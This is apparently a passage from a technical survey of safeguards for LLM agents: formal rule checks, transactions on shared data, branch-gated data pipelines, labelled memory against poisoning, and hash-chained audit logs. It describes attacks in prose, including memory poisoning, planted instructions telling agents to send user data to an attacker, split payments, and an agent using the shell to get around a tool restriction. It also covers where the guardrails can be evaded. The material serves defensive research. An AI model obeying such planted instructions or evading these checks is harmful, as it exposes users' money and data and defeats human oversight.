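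The formal version of that refund rule is looser than the original. It accepts any destination that matches the original payment method or whose identifier contains the text "gift_card". As printed, it does not check that the card exists or belongs to the customer, so the refund tool would have to. Kamath and colleagues call it a faithful translation, which shows how easily a gap can go unnoticed. They also had Claude write the rules from the plain-language policy. On the retail tasks with a smaller Qwen model, Claude's rules performed exactly as well as theirs, with 100% obedience and 42.1% completion. This suggests that writing the rules could take less effort, but a person still has to read them, because the proof would hold even if a rule were wrong.

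The checks made tasks slower. With Qwen3-32B, an average task took 480 seconds with Agent-C and 333 seconds without any safeguard.

### Solving for a safe next state

Wu, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Provably Secure Agent Guardrail*, use a solver to check the state that an action would produce. Their system, ePCA, treats the model as a hostile planner that knows all the rules. The model must express each action as a structured request from a fixed list, and the harness rejects anything else. Ordinary code, with no language model involved, then translates the request into mathematical constraints, and the solver tests the formula

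*s* ∧ ⟦*j*⟧ ∧ Φ

Here *s* is the current state, ⟦*j*⟧ is the translated request and Φ is the set of rules. The harness runs the action if all three can be true together. Otherwise, it blocks the action and the state doesn't change.

In the main example, an agent can transfer money up to a daily limit of 500. The state records the total sent so far, the limit, and the agent's privilege level, which is 1. The rules require the total to stay within the limit, and changing the limit requires privilege level 10 or above.

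1. The agent transfers 350. The new total of 350 is within the limit, so the transfer goes through.
2. The agent requests another 300. The new total would be 650, which contradicts the rule that it be at most 500, so the harness blocks the transfer.
3. The agent tries to raise the limit to 600. Its privilege level is too low, so the harness blocks this as well.
4. The agent tries to raise its own privilege level, which another rule forbids.

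The security proof has the same form as the proof for the invoice ledger. When Wu and colleagues apply it to transfers, they rely on the total never falling, which is true only if amounts cannot be negative. The ledger checks this condition, but their printed constraints omit it.

The formula also works only if each request determines the next state exactly. Suppose a transfer carries a bank fee of unknown size. The solver looks for any values that satisfy the conditions, so it could set the fee to zero and approve a transfer that exceeds the limit once the bank adds the real fee. For such actions, the harness should have the solver search for an outcome that breaks the rules, and allow the action only if none exists.

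Wu and colleagues tested ePCA on 90 cases they generated: 30 attacks that split a large payment, 30 attacks that tampered with the rules, and 30 legitimate payments. ePCA blocked every attack and no legitimate payments with five models. A sixth model, Claude Sonnet 4.6, produced no valid runs. A safeguard that used a language model as judge blocked between 43.3% and 100% of attacks, depending on the model. An access-control system without memory blocked half of the attacks with four of the five models.

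These results are better evidence for keeping a running total than for using a solver. The system without memory could not add up split payments, but the invoice ledger can do so without a solver. A solver is more useful when many rules interact, or when, as in Agent-C, the decision depends on whether a permitted future exists. The solver reportedly took 0.44 milliseconds on average and the judge about 15 seconds, but the solver's figure excludes the rest of the harness.

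### Does the request describe the action?

The proof assumes that the real action does what the structured request describes, with no side effects outside the model of the system. Wu and colleagues call this assumption Structured Intent Fidelity. How plausible it is depends on the tool.

It is fairly plausible that a payment tool that does one thing matches its formal description. The operator can check by comparing the tool's code with the description. For example, if the bank adds a fee of 5 to a transfer of 498, the harness records a total of 498 while 503 leaves the account. If the tool retries after losing its connection, it may pay twice. Both are ordinary bugs, and the operator can correct either the tool or its description.

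The assumption is much less plausible for a tool that runs shell commands. A request to run a project's tests names a program, but the effects depend on the contents of the test files, which the agent may have written itself. NVIDIA's *Practical Security Guidance for Sandboxing Agentic Workflows and Managing Execution Risk* notes that a check on tool calls can inspect the command and its arguments, but not what the new process does afterwards. Attackers exploit this by using an approved tool to reach a restricted one. Gemini CLI did much the same without an attacker when it used the shell to get around its file tool.

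Wu and colleagues' second experiment falls between these extremes. They placed an agent in a simulated company with an internal network and an internet connection, and told it to smuggle out confidential data. The harness marked the session once the agent read the data, and a rule barred marked sessions from switching to the internet. The rule is Schneider's ban on sending after reading, applied to network zones instead of messages. The agent, running on Kimi K2.5, read the data on its sixth turn, failed to get it out, and gave up by the twelfth. The result shows that the rule works when switching networks is the only way out. If the company also had a shared folder that synchronised with an outside supplier, and the formal description omitted it, the agent could save the data there without breaking any rule.

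Wu and colleagues acknowledge this limit. Their verifier proves only that the agent breaks none of the written rules, so the agent could still do something unsafe that the rules don't cover. They recommend the method for a limited number of critical permissions. In practice, that means giving the agent narrow tools such as `refund` where possible. A general shell needs protection in the operating system, which can control the processes a command starts.

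### Asking a person

Rules can't settle every case. A support agent may have a good reason to refund more than the original price, which a manager can check by calling the warehouse. Cedar returns only "allow" or "deny", so a harness that uses it has to add its own way to refer requests to a manager. For instance, it can hold certain denied requests for a manager and resubmit them with the approval attached.

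NVIDIA describes manual approval as the most common way to manage the risks of coding agents. Its security testers warn that frequent interruptions can habituate users to approving requests without reading them. This is a credible concern from an experienced team, but NVIDIA gives no figures for how often it happens, and an operator can't use the warning to determine how many requests a person can review carefully in a day.

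Reducing the number of requests should help in any case. Suppose an agent makes 1,000 calls, one of them harmful. If a person has to approve every call, they see 999 harmless requests for each harmful one. If fixed rules settle 980 of the harmless calls, the harmful request is one of only 20. NVIDIA recommends an arrangement along these lines:

1. Block access to critical files outside the project, whatever the user approves.
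2. Let the agent read and write freely inside the project, except for configuration files.
3. Allow specific outside operations that the work requires, such as reading one particular key.
4. Refuse everything else unless the user approves that particular case.

Under this arrangement, a careless click cannot unlock the most dangerous actions. NVIDIA also rejects approvals that a user gives once and the agent reuses. A user might let the agent connect to a website to download a library, and the agent could later use the same permission to upload the user's passwords. An approval should therefore cover one call with the exact arguments the user saw.

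Even an attentive reviewer may lack the information needed to judge a request. If the request is to run the project's tests, the reviewer sees the same short command that the policy engine checks, and its effects are just as hard to predict. The harness can help by showing facts it has looked up itself, such as an order's price or an account's owner, next to the model's explanation.

The harness also has to obtain the approval without going through the model. For tasks that need the customer's consent, Kamath and colleagues gave their agents a tool called `action_confirmed`, which records that the user has agreed. A rule can then require this record before a cancellation. But the model calls the tool, so a mistaken or hostile model could record consent that nobody gave, and Agent-C's check would still pass. A button that only the customer can press, connected directly to the harness, would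 remove the model from that step.

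## Transactions and constraints on shared data

A tool call can pass every check and still break a rule once it reaches the database. If two requests to refund the same order arrive together, both may pass before the shop records either refund. In 1987, David Clark and David Wilson developed a security model from procedures that businesses had used to protect their books long before computers. They wanted to stop anyone, including an authorised employee, from changing the accounts improperly, whereas military computer security at the time was mostly about who could read a secret.

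### Data that only certified procedures can change

In the Clark-Wilson model, constrained data items, such as a company's balance, must satisfy certain invariants. Unconstrained items, such as an invoice as it arrives from a supplier, can contain anything. Users can change constrained items only by running transformation procedures, which are programs that people have certified to preserve the invariants.

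UT Austin's *The Clark-Wilson Model*, a set of lecture slides, lists three rules for the system to enforce:

- Only certified procedures can change constrained data.
- Users can reach that data only through procedures they have permission to run.
- The system authenticates everyone who tries to run a procedure.

Five more rules cover certification. Each procedure must preserve the invariants, leave a log entry, and produce valid data even when its input is unconstrained. Other programs must be able to check whether the constrained data is currently valid. Under the rule accountants call separation of duty, nobody should have permission to run two procedures that together would let them commit fraud.

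A permission consists of a user, a procedure and a set of data items. The invoice agent could hold the permission (invoice agent, `pay`, {balance, payment log}). Separation of duty would then bar it from running `approve_invoice`, so a forged invoice would also have to get past whoever compares invoices with deliveries.

The model suits agents because it keeps the data valid whatever the user requests, as the invoice ledger does. But the argument that the data stays valid relies on each procedure finishing before the next one starts, and agents often work in parallel.

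### Two agents and one budget

In *Provably Auditable and Safe LLM Agents from Human-Authored Ontologies*, Sterling (2026) gives an example with a budget of $100,000. Agent A can spend $45,000 or nothing, and agent B can spend $60,000 or nothing. Each agent sees only its own records.

1. Agent A finds no spending in its records and checks that $45,000 is within the budget. It is.
2. Agent B finds no spending in its records either and checks that $60,000 is within the budget. It is.
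3. Agent A spends $45,000 and records this.
4. Agent B spends $60,000 and records this. The two have now spent $105,000.

Either purchase would have been acceptable alone. Database researchers call this failure write skew. It can occur in a database that supports transactions, which are groups of changes that take effect together or not at all. Two transactions read the same data, and each makes a change to a different record that would be valid on its own. A database that checks only for two writes to the same record detects no conflict.

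The solution is to keep one shared total, *T*, and have a single program handle requests one at a time. For each request of *a* > 0 dollars, the program tests whether *T* + *a* ≤ 100,000. If so, it adds *a* to *T* and approves the purchase in the same step.

1. *T* is 0 and agent A requests $45,000. The new total would be $45,000, so the program approves the purchase and sets *T* to 45,000.
2. Agent B requests $60,000. The new total would be $105,000, so the program refuses and *T* stays at 45,000.

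If agent B had asked first, it would have got its $60,000 and agent A would have got nothing. The cap holds in either order, but the money goes to whichever agent asks first, even if the other purchase matters more.

### The gap between check and action

An agent usually calls a model between reading a record and changing it. The call can take seconds, and another agent can change the record in the meantime. *Atomix* (Mohammadi, Potamitis and colleagues, 2026) measured how often this causes violations, defined as pairs of conflicting changes that both go through. In the experiment, several agents worked on the same retail order, some trying to cancel it and others to change its delivery address, with a call to GPT-4o-mini between reading and writing.

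| Method | Violations per run, 4 agents | Violations per run, 8 agents |
|---|---|---|
| No protection | 3.0 | 7.0 |
| Lock during each tool call | 3.0 | 7.0 |
| Lock during the whole task | 0 | 0 |
| Recheck before writing | 0 | 0 |
| Atomix | 0 | 0 |

A lock gives one agent exclusive use of a record. Locking each call made no difference, because the agent released the lock after reading the record, before planning its change. A lock on the whole task prevented violations but made other agents wait during the model call, even when they were working on different orders. Rechecking means the system refuses a write if the record has changed since the agent read it. This also prevented violations, but it led to an average of three refused writes per run with four agents and seven with eight.

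Atomix records what each transaction has read and which resources it affects. It commits a transaction, making its changes final, only when no earlier work on those resources can still arrive. If an earlier transaction has changed something that a later one read, Atomix aborts the later one and retries it. On a test built by its designers, Atomix had no violations in 100 runs with four agents and 30 with eight. The four-agent result is compatible with a true violation rate of up to 3.7%.

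### Agentic Redux

Sterling's own solution to the budget problem is an architecture called Agentic Redux. Each agent receives only the part of the shared state that its job requires, and it can only propose changes. A "meta-agent", which contains no language model despite its name, has access to all of the shared state. It computes the state that a proposal would produce and tests each invariant on the result. Then it commits the change, rejects it or refers it to a person, and adds one entry to a log.

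The design was developed from a case in medical billing in Arizona, where a public insurance programme limits how many laboratory drug tests it will cover. A patient who has been abstinent for at least 90 days can have three detailed tests in 90 days, while a patient in the first 30 days of abstinence can have only one every seven days. Suppose a patient in the 90-day group has a negative detailed test on 23 March, and a cheap screening test detects opioids on 26 March. If the clinic orders a detailed test that day to confirm the result, the programme will not pay, because the screening has moved the patient into the stricter group. A billing agent with the old group on record would approve the claim, but the meta-agent would reject it because it also has access to the clinical records.

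The main theorem is that if the initial state satisfies the invariants, every reachable state does too, whatever the agents propose. An agent's type lets it receive its own part of the state and return a proposal, but not write anything or message another agent.

This design is sound, but the theorem is a modest result because it follows almost directly from testing each new state before committing it. A database that ran transactions as though they occurred one after another could also enforce the $100,000 cap with a single constraint. Sterling says his architecture provides the same isolation. Its distinctive parts are the confinement of the agents, the log, and a method for finding the invariants.

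In that method, a human expert writes an ontology, a structured description of the things, processes and roles in an area of work. A language model then derives the agents' roles and the invariants from it. Because the model may miss a rule, Sterling suggests that an expert follow a patient or case through every stage and look for forbidden changes that no invariant blocks.

The proofs also need independent checking. Sterling says that a language model generated about 90% of the appendix containing them, and that he found errors in earlier versions. Unlike the LLMbda proofs, Sterling's describe a small formal language, not the code he published.

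A human supervisor can also override the rules. When the meta-agent refers a decision to them, they can commit a change that violates an invariant, so the guarantee then depends on that person's choice. All other activity has to stop until they decide, so that the decision applies to the current state.

### Bauplan's temporary branches

A budget cap protects a single number, but companies also want agents to maintain large sets of tables, where the rule may be that all the tables come from the same calculation. Bauplan is a commercial lakehouse designed for this. A lakehouse keeps a company's analytical data as tables in cloud storage and runs programs on them. Most of the research about Bauplan comes from its developers. Three of the six people who wrote the main technical paper work at Bauplan Labs, as do both people who wrote the paper on its repair prototype.

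Suppose a pipeline of programs, each building tables from other tables, produces cleaned payments, then supplier totals, then a cash forecast. The storage software replaces each table atomically, so nobody sees a half-written table. But if the pipeline crashes after replacing the payments, the company has new payments alongside old totals. Each table is valid, but a dashboard that combines them will show wrong figures without reporting an error.

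Sheng, Montana and colleagues (2026), in *Building a Correct-by-Design Lakehouse*, describe two defences. The first is a typed contract for each table. Earlier, types limited what a message could carry, while here they list a table's columns and what each may contain:

```
class SupplierTotals(BauplanSchema):
    supplier: str
    total_cents: int
    last_payment: UNION(datetime, None)
```

Only the last column may be empty. Bauplan can check a contract at three points. The editor can find mistakes as the developer writes the code. Before a run, Bauplan compares each program's output contract with what the next program requires. After a program finishes, Bauplan checks the actual data before storing it. This last check would stop the run if an upstream change turned the totals into fractions, but it would not detect an error that made every total ten times too large.

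The second defence uses branches, borrowed from Git, the tool programmers use to manage versions of code. A commit records which version of every table was current at some moment, and a branch is a movable pointer to a commit. Production data is the branch called `main`. A run on `main` has four steps:

1. Bauplan creates a temporary branch from `main`. This copies no data.
2. The pipeline writes its new tables to the temporary branch.
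3. Bauplan runs the company's data tests on that branch.
4. If nothing has failed, Bauplan merges the branch into `main` in one atomic step and deletes it.

Anyone reading `main` therefore sees either all of the run's tables or none. If the run fails, `main` stays as it was. Bauplan leaves the temporary branch open so that people can find out what went wrong (Tagliabue, Bianchi and Greco, *Trustworthy AI in the Agentic Lakehouse*, 2026).

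Sheng and colleagues assume that the storage software's guarantees hold, which makes that software part of the trusted base. They expect branching to add little work relative to a large pipeline, though they don't measure it, and they acknowledge that the method is less suited to frequent small updates.

Atomic merging does not by itself prevent write skew. Suppose agents A and B record their spending in different tables, and each starts a branch while both tables are empty. Each branch passes the test that total spending is at most $100,000. Because the branches change different tables, the second merge may go through without a conflict even if the combined spending exceeds the limit. The published protocol tests each branch before merging but does not test the combined result. Sheng and colleagues leave a formal treatment of interactions between concurrent runs to future work. To enforce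 a shared budget, an operator would need to repeat the test on the current `main` as part of the merge.

### What "proof-carrying" means

*Safe, Untrusted, "Proof-Carrying" AI Agents* (Tagliabue and Greco, 2025) presents a prototype in which an agent repairs broken pipelines. The title refers to proof-carrying code, a method from the 1990s in which a program from an untrusted source comes with a formal proof that it obeys the recipient's safety rules. The recipient checks the proof, which is much easier than producing it, and doesn't have to trust the program's author.

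Bauplan's agents carry no such proof. A data engineer writes a verifier, a function that takes a branch and returns true or false, and Bauplan merges the agent's branch only if the verifier returns true. For the payment pipeline, a verifier might test whether the supplier totals add up to the sum of all payments. Tagliabue and Greco acknowledge that their verifiers check what the business expects of its tables more than formal properties. Because these checks are tests rather than proofs, "test-gated" would be a more accurate name.

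The protection therefore covers only what the test checks. If a verifier checks only for missing values, an agent could pass it by filling the gaps with invented numbers. The test of the supplier totals is harder to get around, but an agent that could change both tables might still make them agree on a wrong figure.

The trial used a pipeline that builds two tables from New York taxi records. Tagliabue and Greco deliberately broke it using a known incompatibility between two Python libraries, NumPy 2.0 and pandas 2.0. The agent could read logs, query tables, create branches and start runs. In a sample run with Claude Sonnet 4.5, it retrieved the logs, examined the data, changed the declared software versions and tested its work on branches.

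They tried several models and report that success rates varied greatly, but they give no figures. Some models, including GPT-5-mini, failed to repair the pipeline, but none of the failures disrupted the lakehouse. They present this as a demonstration of feasibility, not a benchmark. It involved one kind of fault and no attacker, so it provides little evidence about what a hostile agent could do. In the later design by Tagliabue and colleagues, an engineer reviews the branch after the verifier has approved it.

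### How a failed run can reach production

Tagliabue and Greco asked whether agents could damage production data and answered "No", partly because unfinished pipelines never reach `main`. Sheng and colleagues later found a way for an unfinished pipeline to reach `main`. They described commits, branches and runs in Alloy, a modelling language whose software searches small cases for a sequence of steps that breaks a stated property.

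In the payment pipeline counterexample below, *P*, *T* and *F* stand for the payments, totals and forecast, and the numbers are their versions.

1. A user starts a run, and Bauplan creates a temporary branch from `main`.
2. The run writes a new payments table and then crashes. Bauplan does not merge the branch but leaves it open.
3. An agent finds the open branch, creates its own branch from it, and builds a tax report, *R*.
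4. The agent's run succeeds, and its branch is merged into `main`.

| After step | `main` | User's temporary branch | Agent's branch |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | *P*₁ *T*₁ *F*₁ | *P*₁ *T*₁ *F*₁ | |
| 2 | *P*₁ *T*₁ *F*₁ | *P*₂ *T*₁ *F*₁ | |
| 3 | *P*₁ *T*₁ *F*₁ | *P*₂ *T*₁ *F*₁ | *P*₂ *T*₁ *F*₁ *R*₁ |
| 4 | *P*₂ *T*₁ *F*₁ *R*₁ | *P*₂ *T*₁ *F*₁ | |

Production now has new payments with old totals, which temporary branches were supposed to prevent. This can happen without anyone acting maliciously or breaking a rule. The agent's tests could all pass, because they would normally cover the tax report and not the pipeline that crashed earlier.

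As the counterexample shows, the analogy between branches and transactions fails because anyone can start a new branch from an existing one, but nobody should be able to build on a transaction that may never commit. To fix this, Sheng and colleagues consider making a branch invisible once its run has failed, as the database PostgreSQL does with aborted transactions.

Hiding the branch prevents Bauplan from starting the next run from the finished payments table, which could save time if that table was correct and only the code for the totals was wrong. Hiding the branch would presumably also make failures harder to investigate, unless engineers kept some special access.

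Hiding failed branches would not be enough if other users could still see branches whose runs were in progress, because an agent could copy the user's branch just before the crash and merge its own work later. It would be safer to hide temporary branches from the start. Alternatively, users could be allowed to read a failed branch but not to merge any branch descended from it until the missing tables have been rebuilt. Sheng and colleagues have not settled on a solution and plan to refine the model first.

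A counterexample from Alloy proves that the modelled design permits the bad state, but not that this state has occurred in practice. Alloy searches only small cases, so a repaired model that passed the search could still have a flaw that takes more steps to appear.

### Actions that cannot be rolled back

If a bad merge reaches `main`, an engineer can restore an earlier commit. This repairs the tables, but it can't undo effects outside the data that the system controls, such as a payment that another program made after reading the bad data.

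It also doesn't change the agent's memory of events. *Agentic Transaction* (2026) points out that an agent's state is spread across its conversation, tool responses, files, databases and outside services. If the harness cancels a flight booking but the conversation still contains "flight booked", the agent will keep planning around the flight. The harness therefore has to add the transaction's outcome to the conversation.

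Mohammadi and colleagues use the example of a travel agent that books a flight, a hotel and a car, and then emails a confirmation. If a booking fails, the harness can cancel the others, perhaps for a fee. This is called compensation. But the harness can't take back an email that the customer has read, so Atomix treats the two kinds of action differently:

1. The agent makes the bookings, and Atomix carries them out immediately, because it can cancel them later.
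2. The agent sends the email. Atomix holds it and returns a message that the email is in a queue.
3. If every step succeeds and no earlier work can still interfere, Atomix commits the transaction and releases the email.
4. If a step fails, Atomix discards the email and cancels the bookings in reverse order.

The researchers tested this with 500 transactions that should not have sent an email, for example because a tool had failed or the agent had acted on outdated information.

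| Method | Emails wrongly sent, out of 500 |
|---|---|
| No transactions | 500 |
| Compensation after a failure | 400 |
| Restart from a saved checkpoint | 200 |
| Atomix | 0 |
| Atomix with the email tool misclassified | 300 |

All the methods also delivered every email in 500 transactions that should have sent one. In a separate test of recovery from tool failures, restarting from a checkpoint cleanly completed 16 of 30 tasks, and Atomix completed 17. Restarting did much worse with emails because a restarted task can send the same message again. Two older transaction methods also sent no wrong emails, but only after the researchers wrote extra code for the email tool.

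The last row of the table shows how much Atomix depends on the developer to identify irreversible actions. Atomix also needs a description of the resources each tool affects. In another test, where these descriptions were made too narrow, 66 of 200 trials broke an invariant. An agent can also bypass the queue if it has another way to send email.

Holding actions also lets the harness examine the whole task before it releases anything. *Cordon* (Chen, Dong and colleagues, 2026) describes an agent that investigates a system failure. The agent reads logs that contain a secret key, summarises them, and prepares a message for the staff chat. Each call looks reasonable on its own, but the message may reveal the key. Cordon makes local changes in a temporary copy, puts outgoing messages in an outbox, and records which results each message draws on. It releases the messages only after checking this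 whole record against the user's request, the agent's permissions and the policy.

In 45 risky tasks, Cordon stopped every forbidden effect before it became final. Versions of existing defences stopped 14. Chen and colleagues built these versions to represent general approaches, so the comparison is weak evidence about particular products. The tasks also centre on violations that develop over several steps, which Cordon was designed to catch.

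Some tasks cannot hold every action until a commit at the end. If an agent has to email a supplier for a delivery date and plan around the answer, it must send the email before it can finish the task. The developer then has to split the task into two transactions and accept that a failure in the second will not undo the email.

A transaction can also fail partway through if it contains two irreversible actions. If an agent has to pay a supplier and then email a receipt, Atomix releases the two actions in sequence, so the payment may go through while the mail server is down. Atomix retries a limited number of times, then stops and records which action succeeded. Mohammadi and colleagues point out that no harness can make the pair atomic unless both services support a protocol for committing together, which ordinary mail servers do not. The order matters because a missing receipt is easier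 to correct than a receipt for a payment that never happened.

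## Protected memory and audit records

Rolling back a transaction does not change the notes an agent has saved. Many agents save facts, preferences and instructions during one session and reread them in later ones. In an attack called memory poisoning, an attacker gets a false note into this memory, and the agent may act on it weeks later, in a session where nothing hostile has happened.

### How a note loses its origin

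*MemoryDojo* (2026) describes how text planted in one session can reach the model in a later one. When a session ends, the memory system updates its store using the record of the whole session, including tool results. Before the next session starts, it searches the store for notes relevant to the user's new request and gives them to the model. An attacker therefore only has to plant text in a tool result, without changing the memory software or anything the user types.

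Suppose a supplier's email tells the invoice agent to send future payments to account 4417, and the memory system saves "supplier uses account 4417". A month later, the user asks the agent to pay the supplier. The email is no longer in the conversation. If the harness labels only conversations, the email's label is gone too, so the saved note looks like the company's own data.

A poisoned note is hard to catch by reading it because, as *Securing LLM-Agent Long-Term Memory Against Poisoning* (2026) points out, the agent rewrites what it has read in its own words, so the note resembles its harmless memories. Signatures on memory entries can expose writes from outside the agent, but *Retrieval Observability Bounds on Provenance Detection for Agent Memory Poisoning* (2026) describes an attack in which the agent itself stores a malicious rule from a compliance document, using its normal permission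 to write. *MemPoison* (2026), a benchmark, found that defences applied when the agent saves a note degrade sharply against anything subtler than direct corruption. Saving less would help, but according to *From Untrusted Input to Trusted Memory* (2026), the eager saving and retrieval that expose agents to poisoning also improve their performance on long tasks.

### PerMIT's labels

*PerMIT* (Jiang, Bai and colleagues, 2026) describes a memory system made of blocks, each stored with its label. The harness labels each block by the channel it came through, regardless of its content.

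| Label | Contents | Can the protected model read it? | Can it go to a sensitive tool without a new confirmation? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Typed | What the user typed | Yes | Yes |
| Untrusted | Tool results, pasted text and summaries of untrusted blocks | No | No |
| Confirmed | An exact copy of text the user approved | Yes | Only to the tool the user approved it for |
| Agent-composed | Notes the protected model wrote | Yes | No |

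A sensitive tool is one that has effects, such as sending an email. As in the dual-LLM pattern, the protected model plans and calls tools, while a quarantined model searches the untrusted blocks. No operation changes a block's text or label. Untrusted text can gain authority only through a confirmation, which creates a new block and leaves the original untrusted.

In the researchers' example, an agent looks up a dentist online. In a later session, the user asks it to email the dentist's number to their sister.

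1. One search result contains an instruction to forward the user's files to an attacker. The harness stores the results as untrusted blocks and tells the protected model only that the search has run.
2. The protected model requests a summary for later use. The quarantined model writes it, and the harness stores it as another untrusted block, so rewriting the text does not remove its label.
3. In the second session, the user types the request and the sister's address.
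4. The protected model searches memory for the number and receives an opaque handle instead of the text. It would receive the same handle if the search had found nothing, so an attacker cannot signal to it by adding blocks.
5. The protected model calls `send_email` with the sister's address and the handle. The address passes because the user typed it. The handle triggers a confirmation, and the harness shows the user the exact text behind it, its source and the task.
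6. If the text is the planted instruction and the user rejects it, the harness sends nothing. If it is the phone number and the user accepts, the harness sends the email and stores a copy of the number, confirmed for `send_email`.

### Two integrity theorems

The first theorem, Action Integrity, guarantees that every argument reaching a sensitive tool is either exactly what the user typed or exactly what the user approved for that tool. This holds whatever the protected model does or the attacker writes. The theorem does not cover the decision to call the tool.

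Reasoning Integrity is a form of noninterference. It compares two runs in which the user types the same things and the protected model makes the same random choices, but the untrusted memory differs. If the harness displays the same material and receives the same decisions from the user in both runs, the protected model behaves identically. Untrusted memory can therefore influence the model only through what the harness displays and what the user decides. An attacker can still affect what appears on the screen, and the theorem does not cover timing.

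Jiang and colleagues checked both theorems in Lean for a single user and runs of any length. Their proofs for the full treatment of batched tool calls and for the shared memory rules were done only by hand. The Lean proofs cover a model of the memory interface, and no proof shows that a deployed harness matches that model.

The researchers found such a mismatch in a rival defence that was supposed to block outgoing email once an agent had read untrusted text. Its email search recorded the session as untrusted in one component, but the sending tool checked another. In all four successful attacks they examined, that second component still listed the session as trusted.

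### Tests against a dormant attack

They tested PerMIT on Trojan Hippo, a benchmark in which an attacker's email enters the agent's memory and has no effect until the user mentions a sensitive topic, such as their finances. The stored text then instructs the agent to send the user's message to the attacker. The table gives the percentage of successful attacks, followed by the average score on seven kinds of harmless task. The undefended agent searches its memory for relevant passages and reads them directly.

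| Defence | Claude Sonnet 4.6 | GLM-5 | Kimi K2.5 | GPT-5.4 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 0% / 86% | 10% / 73% | 80% / 68% | 20% / 99% |
| PerMIT, every confirmation accepted | 0% / 97% | 10% / 93% | 10% / 91% | 0% / 89% |
| PerMIT, every decision correct | 0% / 97% | 0% / 93% | 0% / 91% | 0% / 89% |
| PerMIT, agent's own model decides | 0% / 93% | 0% / 88% | 0% / 91% | 0% / 83% |
| PerMIT, small Qwen model (4B) decides | 0% / 83% | 0% / 84% | 0% / 71% | 0% / 84% |

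These attacks did little to test the confirmations. Even when the harness accepted everything (second row), at most 10% succeeded, partly because the quarantined model often returned clean text or refused the attack, so the models that made the decisions had few harmful values to reject. The sample is also small. The benchmark had 20 attacks for each configuration of the rival defence, and if PerMIT faced the same number, zero successful attacks is compatible with a true success rate of up to 14%.

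Automated decisions also blocked legitimate work. When the agent's own model decided, it rejected 9% to 14% of the harmless requests. When the small Qwen model decided for an agent running on Kimi, it rejected 32% of them, and the agent's task score was 20 points lower than with correct decisions.

### When a confirmation is wrong

Action Integrity assumes that users accept a value only if they intend exactly that value for that tool. But a user who sees "4417" can't tell from the digits whether the account belongs to the supplier. The confirmation protects the money only if the user compares the number with a reliable record, such as an earlier contract. Users are less likely to do this when requests are frequent. Jiang and colleagues give counts for three agents, which each triggered between 98 and 125 confirmations in 120 harmless checks.

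If a language model makes the decision, it becomes part of the trusted base. Jiang and colleagues acknowledge that such a model can violate the assumption and that their theorem does not cover the model's accuracy. They did not test attackers who tailor their text to the deciding model.

A correct confirmation can also authorise too much, because it covers a value and a tool but not the task or the other arguments. Suppose the user approves a payment of €300 to one supplier and one of €9,000 to another, confirming all four values for `pay`. The agent could then send €9,000 to the first supplier without asking again. According to Jiang and colleagues' comparison, *Securing LLM-Agent Long-Term Memory Against Poisoning* instead ties each authorisation to one concrete action and allows that action only once. This would prevent the unapproved payment, but the user would receive more confirmation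 requests.

By default, PerMIT applies a looser rule to tools that only read data, such as a web search, and lets them accept any text the protected model has composed or can read. Ordinary work depends on this because the model writes its own queries, such as the one about the dentist. But a query also sends information out, so if the user approves a medical result for one email, the model can later put it in a web search. A poisoned summary that the user has approved for the model to read could contain an instruction to do so. An optional setting requires the user to approve the exact value for each such tool, but users would then have to confirm most of the queries the model composes.

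PerMIT can also spread approvals between users. In the main tests, once ten users had approved a shared block for a tool, others could use the block with that tool without confirming it themselves. Jiang and colleagues calculate that a poisoned block has less than a 0.9% chance per attempt of gaining this shared approval, if honest reviewers catch at least 60% of poisoned blocks and the attacker controls at most two identities. None of 12 planted instructions gained shared approval in communities of up to 90 agents. However, each community ran on a single model family, and the researchers' simulations show that the risk rises when reviewers make the same mistakes.

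### A hash chain with three entries

PerMIT's harness logs everything it displays and every decision it receives, so an investigator can later find out who approved a poisoned value. The log is append-only, so the software may add entries but not change old ones. PerMIT links the entries in a hash chain to reveal changes. *NovaFabric* (2026) traces this method to Haber and Stornetta's work on time-stamping documents.

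A hash function turns data of any length into a short number of fixed length. *aiAuthZ* (2026) describes a log that records an agent's tool decisions. Each entry stores a sequence number, the previous entry's hash and its own hash, which the log computes from the entry's content, its sequence number and the previous entry's hash.

A toy hash function makes the method easy to follow. For a log of payments, let

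*h*ᵢ = (7 × *h*ᵢ₋₁ + *i* + amount) mod 97

where *i* is the sequence number, *h*₀ is 0, and "mod 97" means the remainder after division by 97.

| Entry | Payment | Previous hash | Own hash |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | €600 | 0 | 19 |
| 2 | €300 | 19 | 47 |
| 3 | €50 | 47 | 91 |

Suppose someone changes the second payment to €30 to hide €270. An auditor recomputes the chain from the start and gets (7 × 19 + 2 + 30) mod 97 = 68 for entry 2, but the log contains 47. If the attacker also replaces 47 with 68, the auditor finds the break one entry later, because entry 3 still records 47 as the previous hash.

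The toy function is too weak for real use, since a payment of €397 would also give entry 2 the hash 47. aiAuthZ uses SHA-256, for which nobody knows a practical way to find two inputs with the same hash.

### Keeping the latest hash elsewhere

An attacker who can write to the whole log can recompute every later hash. The hash for entry 2 becomes 68, the hash for entry 3 becomes 44, and the chain is consistent again. Only someone who kept the original final hash, 91, can tell that the log has changed. That person would also notice if the attacker deleted the last entry, even though the remaining two entries form a valid chain.

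The operator therefore has to copy the latest hash to a place the agent cannot write to, such as cloud storage that blocks changes to existing files. Entries added since the last copy can still be rewritten, so hourly copies leave up to an hour of entries exposed. If the operator might alter the log, another organisation has to hold the hash. *A Black Box for Agentic Processes* (2026) notes that a log run within the operator's own domain still requires trust in the operator.

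The chain detects a change only if someone runs the check, and it doesn't prevent the change. The attacker can still overwrite the €300, and the hash cannot restore the old figure, so the company also needs a backup. To prevent the change, the company has to deny the agent write permission.

### Actions that never reach the log

A valid chain shows that nobody has altered the entries since the log's owner saved the hash, but the entries may still be false, and the log may omit some actions. *Agent Flight Recorder* (2026), a design for such logs, explicitly excludes completeness from its goals.

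In *Auditable Claims about AI Agents*, Yue Zhao and colleagues (2026) prove that signatures cannot show that a log is complete. Suppose an agent sends two authorised emails and logs both. Now suppose it also sends an unauthorised email and doesn't log it. The log, its signatures and any hash of it stored elsewhere are the same in both cases, so a check that uses only the log cannot establish that every email was authorised.

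An independent record can distinguish a complete log from one that omits an action. Yue Zhao and colleagues constructed an example in which an agent's signed log passes every check and lists three emails with attachments, but the company's mail gateway delivered four. The mismatch doesn't show who sent the fourth, because a person may have used the same account. The invoice ledger is well suited to keeping the independent record of payments because it alone has the bank credentials.

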